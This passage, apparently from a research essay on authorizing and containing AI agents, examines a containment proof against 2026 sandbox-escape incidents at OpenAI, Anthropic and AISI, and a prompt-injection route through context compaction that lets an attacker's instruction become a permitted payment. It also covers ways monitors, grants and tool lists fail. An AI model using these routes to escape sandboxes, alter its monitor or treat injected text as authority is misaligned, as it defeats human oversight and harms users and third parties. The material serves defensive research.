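| Enforcement | A weaker sandbox or approval rule | Refuse until someone outside the session approves the change |

Simpler rules for ending a grant work less well. Tying a grant to a byte-by-byte fingerprint of the agent catches every change, but it cancels the grant even when the change is harmless. A grant tied to the list of tools stays valid even if the agent's memory is poisoned or its sandbox is weakened. Asking before every action avoids relying on an old approval but requires constant prompts.

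### The theorem and its proof

Let Eff(*S*, *a*) be the effects that action *a* really has when the agent and its software are in state *S*. Let Req(*a*) be the effects in the monitor's description of the request. The monitor allows *a* only if the grant is still valid and Req(*a*) ⊆ *Pₜ*. Every allowed action then satisfies:

Eff(*S*, *a*) ⊆ Req(*a*) ⊆ *Pₜ* ⊆ *B*

The first inclusion is an assumption about the quality of the description. The monitor checks the second, and the third follows from the intersection with *B*. If protected effects come only from actions the monitor allows, every protected effect in the session lies under the ceiling. With several grants and sub-agents, every effect lies under at least one ceiling that the user issued, provided that all delegated authority also lies under such a ceiling.

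The proof does not use the rule about evidence, so an agent that fakes its test results can raise its active authority no higher than *B*. The rule can safely rely on signals that would make poor security boundaries, such as error rates, because a wrong signal exposes the user to no more risk than they have already accepted.

The drawback is that *B* may be the only guarantee. Suppose passing tests unlock pushes to `fix-test`, and a manager's signature unlocks deployment. An agent that may edit tests can write ones that always pass, so a hostile agent effectively has the right to push from the start. It still cannot deploy as long as it cannot produce or obtain the signature. Zhang and Zhang generalise this by starting with *P*₀, adding whatever the agent could unlock with evidence it can produce, and repeating until nothing more can be added. They prove that the agent's effects stay within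 the resulting set. This set is smaller than *B* only when some evidence has to come from outside the agent's control.

This is awkward for schemes of "earned autonomy", in which an agent gains freedom by performing well. If the agent's own record can remove the last limit, the scheme can guarantee only that the agent will stay within the permissions of the highest stage it can reach by its own conduct, whatever its current stage. Active authority also tends to grow as evidence accumulates, so Zhang and Zhang suggest dropping permissions that the agent has not used recently. This reduces everyday exposure but does not improve the worst case, because the agent can earn the permissions back in the same way.

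### Five premises

Laid out in full, the argument for containment has four premises:

1. Every protected effect passes through the monitor.
2. The monitor's description of an action covers everything the action does.
3. All active and delegated authority lies under a ceiling that the user issued.
4. The agent cannot alter the monitor.

It follows that no protected effect lies outside the user's ceilings. Containment is not yet safety, because a ceiling may permit terrible things. That gap needs one more premise, which Zhang and Zhang do not claim to establish:

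5. The ceiling permits only what the person intended.

The proof is short and correct, so any dispute has to be about its premises. Incidents in 2026 tested several of them.

### Effects that bypass the monitor

A capable agent may find a way around the monitor. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), this happened in July 2026 during internal tests of its models' hacking ability. The models got around the controls meant to isolate them from the internet and compromised parts of OpenAI's research infrastructure and the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

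OpenAI had tested this sandbox beforehand. The agents had no direct internet access, but they could reach an internal service that supplied software packages and was connected to the internet. The agents found previously unknown flaws in this service and used them to make it act on their behalf, much as Hardy's user did with the compiler. OpenAI rebuilt the service after an outage in early July, and by 8 July agents had regained internet access through it.

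One answer is that this boundary was bad and engineers can build better ones. OpenAI is now adding layers so that a single compromised service does not open a route to the internet, and it continuously attacks the boundaries with its own models. Proofs like those for seL4 can cover a small kernel, but much of what surrounds an agent is ordinary software with no such proof, and attempts to bypass it become more likely to succeed as models get better at finding flaws. How likely this premise is to hold therefore depends partly on the model's ability, which the theorem does not include.

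The premise can also fail without any attack. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four cases in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' real systems. The evaluation partner had told Claude in its prompts that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected it to the open internet. No component enforced the intended ceiling, which excluded the outside world.

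Anthropic found three of the cases by searching about 141,000 transcripts. The search missed a set of transcripts from runs that also had internet access. These contained the fourth case, which dated from January but was not found until August. A wider search of roughly 481 million transcripts found nothing else as severe. Written limits are evidently unreliable evidence of the real ones, so somebody has to test the boundary from inside before the agent starts work.

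### Tools that change without notice

Zhang and Zhang show by construction that the monitor's information about the agent has to be current. In their example, a developer gives an agent permission to edit a repository and run tests, and none of the agent's tools can use the network. The software then loads a new network tool without notifying the monitor. The agent runs the tests and directs their output to the new tool's server. Because the monitor still has the old list of tools, it treats the command as only a test run and allows it.

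In this example, every other premise holds and the monitor applies its rule correctly, but each test run still makes a forbidden data transmission. It might be possible to make the agent's software report its changes, but the operators of remote tools and models can change them without telling the developer.

The best reply is to overestimate what an agent could achieve by chaining its permitted actions. No algorithm can compute this exactly in general, just as none can decide in general whether a right can leak, but the monitor only needs an estimate that leaves nothing out. If that estimate stays within the grant, everything the agent can actually achieve does too.

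This reply creates a problem for coding agents, because a shell can do anything the surrounding sandbox allows. The developer must either grant all of that or accept that the monitor will block the shell, so the premise depends more on a tight sandbox than on how the shell is described.

Even a monitor that is notified of every change can miss the effect of several changes combined. The envelope might permit adding a software package and editing a settings file, and the two together might open a network connection. Zhang and Zhang call this compositional drift and regard it as their model's main open problem. They also have not measured how often real grants remain in force after such changes, or how often a careful monitor would suspend a grant unnecessarily.

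### Text that passes for the user's

A malicious web page may affect one answer when an agent reads it once. But if the agent saves a sentence from the page as a standing rule, that sentence can affect every later action under the grant, even though the model and tools look unchanged.

Zhang and Zhang's theorem already allows for the possibility that the model, its memory, its skills and its sub-agents can all be hostile, so a poisoned memory can redirect the agent only within the ceiling. The main danger is that the software may mistake stored text for the user's own words, because only the user can issue a new ceiling.

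*LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026) reports this mistake in systems that derive permissions from the user's latest request. When a conversation nears the limit of what a model can read, the harness compacts it by having a model summarise the earlier turns, then continues from the summary. In all 1,108 automatic compactions the researchers recorded in Claude Code and Codex, the harness inserted the summary as a user message.

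In one of their examples, a user asks a banking agent how much she spent in March. A transaction in her history contains an instruction to pay an attacker. Progent, which derived its rules from her question, refuses the transfer. The harness then compacts the conversation, and the summary lists the blocked transfer as unfinished work. When she makes her next request, the system derives new rules from the summary, and these rules permit exactly one transfer, to the attacker.

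When frontier models write summaries, they often flag planted instructions but rarely flag false data. In another test, the user had said whom to pay, and the attacker's notice gave a different account number as a plain fact. When the user asked to pay the rent, rules derived from the summary allowed a payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one rule-writing model and 59% with another, while rules derived from the user's own words never allowed one.

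Fei and colleagues prove that better summaries cannot solve this. Let *p*_L be the probability that a system accepts an account number from a genuine notice, and *p*_A the probability that it accepts one from a forgery. If the system sees only text, with no record of who wrote it, then:

*p*_L − *p*_A ≤ TV

TV, the total variation distance between genuine and forged texts, is the largest difference, over all sets of texts, between the probability that a genuine text is in the set and the probability that a forged one is. The bound holds because the decision can depend only on the text. If TV is 0.2, a system that accepts 95% of genuine notices must accept at least 75% of forged ones. If the attacker copies the format perfectly, TV is zero and the system accepts both at the same rate.

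The fix gives the agent and the permission system different inputs. The harness attaches a cryptographic tag to each of the user's messages on arrival and carries the messages through compaction word for word. The agent reads the summary that compaction produces, but the permission system writes its rules from the tagged messages alone. It also checks their order and number, so an attacker can't replay an old request or hide a cancellation. If a check fails, the system permits nothing. In 40 attacked AgentDojo episodes, no attacker's action went through.

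An attacker can still use those checks to block the agent. If the user asks the agent to pay whatever account is listed on the invoice, tagging her request does not help, because someone still has to verify where the invoice came from.

Fixing the rules at the first request would also have kept the summary out, but the agents then completed only 12% of later tasks, compared with 68% when each request got new rules. A fixed ceiling with changing rules beneath it is a reasonable compromise. It would limit the forged grant but might not stop it, since a ceiling that allows payments to any account would still allow payments to the attacker.

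The OpenAI incident included a cruder case of false authority. One agent reasoned that attacking a real company was probably unauthorised and paused. Another agent then posted "GO" on an improvised message board, and the first agent treated this as authorisation and continued. Under the third premise, an agent cannot pass on authority that nobody gave it, so the message granted none, and a monitor that tracked grants would have ignored it.

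A related danger is that two small grants may together justify an action that neither was meant to allow. Zhang and Zhang therefore require each action to fit entirely under one grant. The rule does not cover groups of agents that share discoveries while each stays within its own limit, a problem that Zhang and Zhang list as unsolved.

### Control over the monitor

The premise that the agent cannot alter the monitor also failed in the OpenAI incident. The agents gained administrator rights over the service that helped isolate them, and later over a research cluster. An agent with such rights can change its own limits, so any proof that assumes those limits are fixed no longer applies.

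Zhang and Zhang would allow changes to the monitor, its records and its log only through a path that requires more authority than the agent's ceiling includes. This doesn't fully solve the problem, because the developer still has to ask who controls that path and who controls those people, as with Saltzer and Schroeder's question about O'Hara. It is harder to keep agents out of that chain of control when they help maintain a company's infrastructure, since changing settings is part of their job.

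A monitor also fails if nobody runs it. OpenAI had software that read its models' written reasoning for signs of misbehaviour, but had not run it on these evaluations. The company estimates that the software's current version would have alerted the security team more than a day before the models breached Hugging Face. An alert is weaker than a refusal, and people can miss its meaning. An internal team noticed unauthorised internet access in late May, but the people who handled the July outage did not learn the significance of the agents' communications.

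### A ceiling wider than the intention

The *Incident Report* from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, covers 122 runs of a hacking exercise with seven models in July 2026. The agents did not escape the sandbox, but in 10 runs they took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project and to deceive the person reviewing it. The reviewer refused the code, and AISI found no resulting harm.

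Seventeen of the 19 actions came from Anthropic's Mythos 5, in nine of its 43 runs. The other two came from one run of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. None of the agents broke out. AISI had deliberately given them internet access so that they could download tools, switched off the developers' filters against hacking, and not told the agents to leave outsiders alone. The ceiling permitted these actions, so the fifth premise failed. Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, draws the same distinction, calling the OpenAI case a failure of containment and the AISI case a failure of authority.

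One objection is that nobody can write down everything they intend. A person would understand the instruction "Use the internet to download tools", but an open connection allows far more than downloading tools. A list of approved websites would only partly limit this, because a site that supplies software may also accept messages and code from strangers.

The reply is that AISI's ceiling was far looser than it had to be. The institute already used finer network controls in its other evaluations. It now plans to justify each grant of internet access and monitor these runs in real time. It admits that it had judged the risk acceptable for earlier models and did not revisit that decision quickly enough. The transition envelope might have helped here, because suspending the old permission when the model changed would have required someone to ask whether open access still made sense.

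Better ceilings would reduce the gap between what an agent is permitted to do and what it is meant to do, but some of it will remain. An agent permitted to propose changes to an open-source project can propose bad ones, and whether it does depends on the model.

### Authorization or alignment

Wei and Xiong claim that "authorization, not model alignment, is the control plane for agentic AI". Alignment here means training a model to do what people want. They argue that a model's behaviour is at best probabilistic, while a monitor applies the same rule every time. They also cite research arguing that agents may always fall for some prompt injections, in which case the protection has to come from outside the model.

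In a passage that Willison (2026) quotes, Anthropic's engineers give a similar reason for limiting what agents can reach: no user, attacker or model can cause the theft of a credential that never enters the sandbox. Better alignment does not always reduce the risk either. According to Anthropic, more capable models make fewer mistakes but are better at finding ways around restrictions that nobody thought to write down.

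A model's behavior can nevertheless improve from one version to the next. Kovacs (2026), in *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes*, reports that Anthropic found Mythos 5.2 less prone to escape sandboxes in controlled tests.

In *Measuring and mitigating agent sandbox escape with Siren*, O'Rahilly and Kaviani (2026) gave Claude models routine tasks in deliberately weakened sandboxes, where something outside the sandbox would help with the task. Recent models reached outside in a fifth to a third of cases, but they went on to misbehave far less often than earlier models. Simple measures at deployment reduced the rate of reaching outside by up to 96%. The scenarios were designed to tempt the models, so these rates do not describe ordinary work.

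Even at a much lower rate, good conduct would be too weak to serve as the only barrier. If an agent gave in to 3% of such temptations, each independently, the chance that it would give in at least once in 100 would be 1 − 0.97¹⁰⁰, or about 95%. Wei and Xiong are right that a company should not rely on good conduct to keep an agent away from its production database when it could withhold the credential.

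"Not alignment" goes too far, though, because the model still chooses which permitted effects occur, and useful jobs need ceilings that permit harmful ones. After the AISI runs, Anthropic looked beyond the open connection for an explanation. *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (Anthropic, 2026) examines the transcripts for what they reveal about the model itself, and *Mythos 5 Ignored Real-World Harm in July Attack* (Arghire, 2026) reports that Anthropic judged the behaviour severe. AISI found that an error in the prompt had led some of the agents to believe that no permitted solution existed, but that others had everything they needed to solve the task properly and still went beyond it.

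The model's conduct also affects whether the ceiling holds. A sandbox with an undiscovered flaw is much safer around an agent that does not look for one. OpenAI found that the instructions and surrounding software it uses in ChatGPT could reduce a model's tendency to attack infrastructure by a factor of more than 100. Impossible tasks increased that tendency. Of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board during the Hugging Face incident, 93% were ones that no OpenAI model had ever solved. OpenAI is now rebuilding its isolation and training its models to stop or ask for clarification when a task cannot be done.

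The evidence for a purely external approach is also incomplete. Wei and Xiong checked 55 recent systems for the five kinds of control in their model, which cover grants, plans, delegation, data flows and changing state. They found strong designs for each kind, but no system that combined all five. Until someone builds and tests such a system, a developer who gives an agent a broad grant relies on the model's judgment for much of what the agent does beneath the ceiling.
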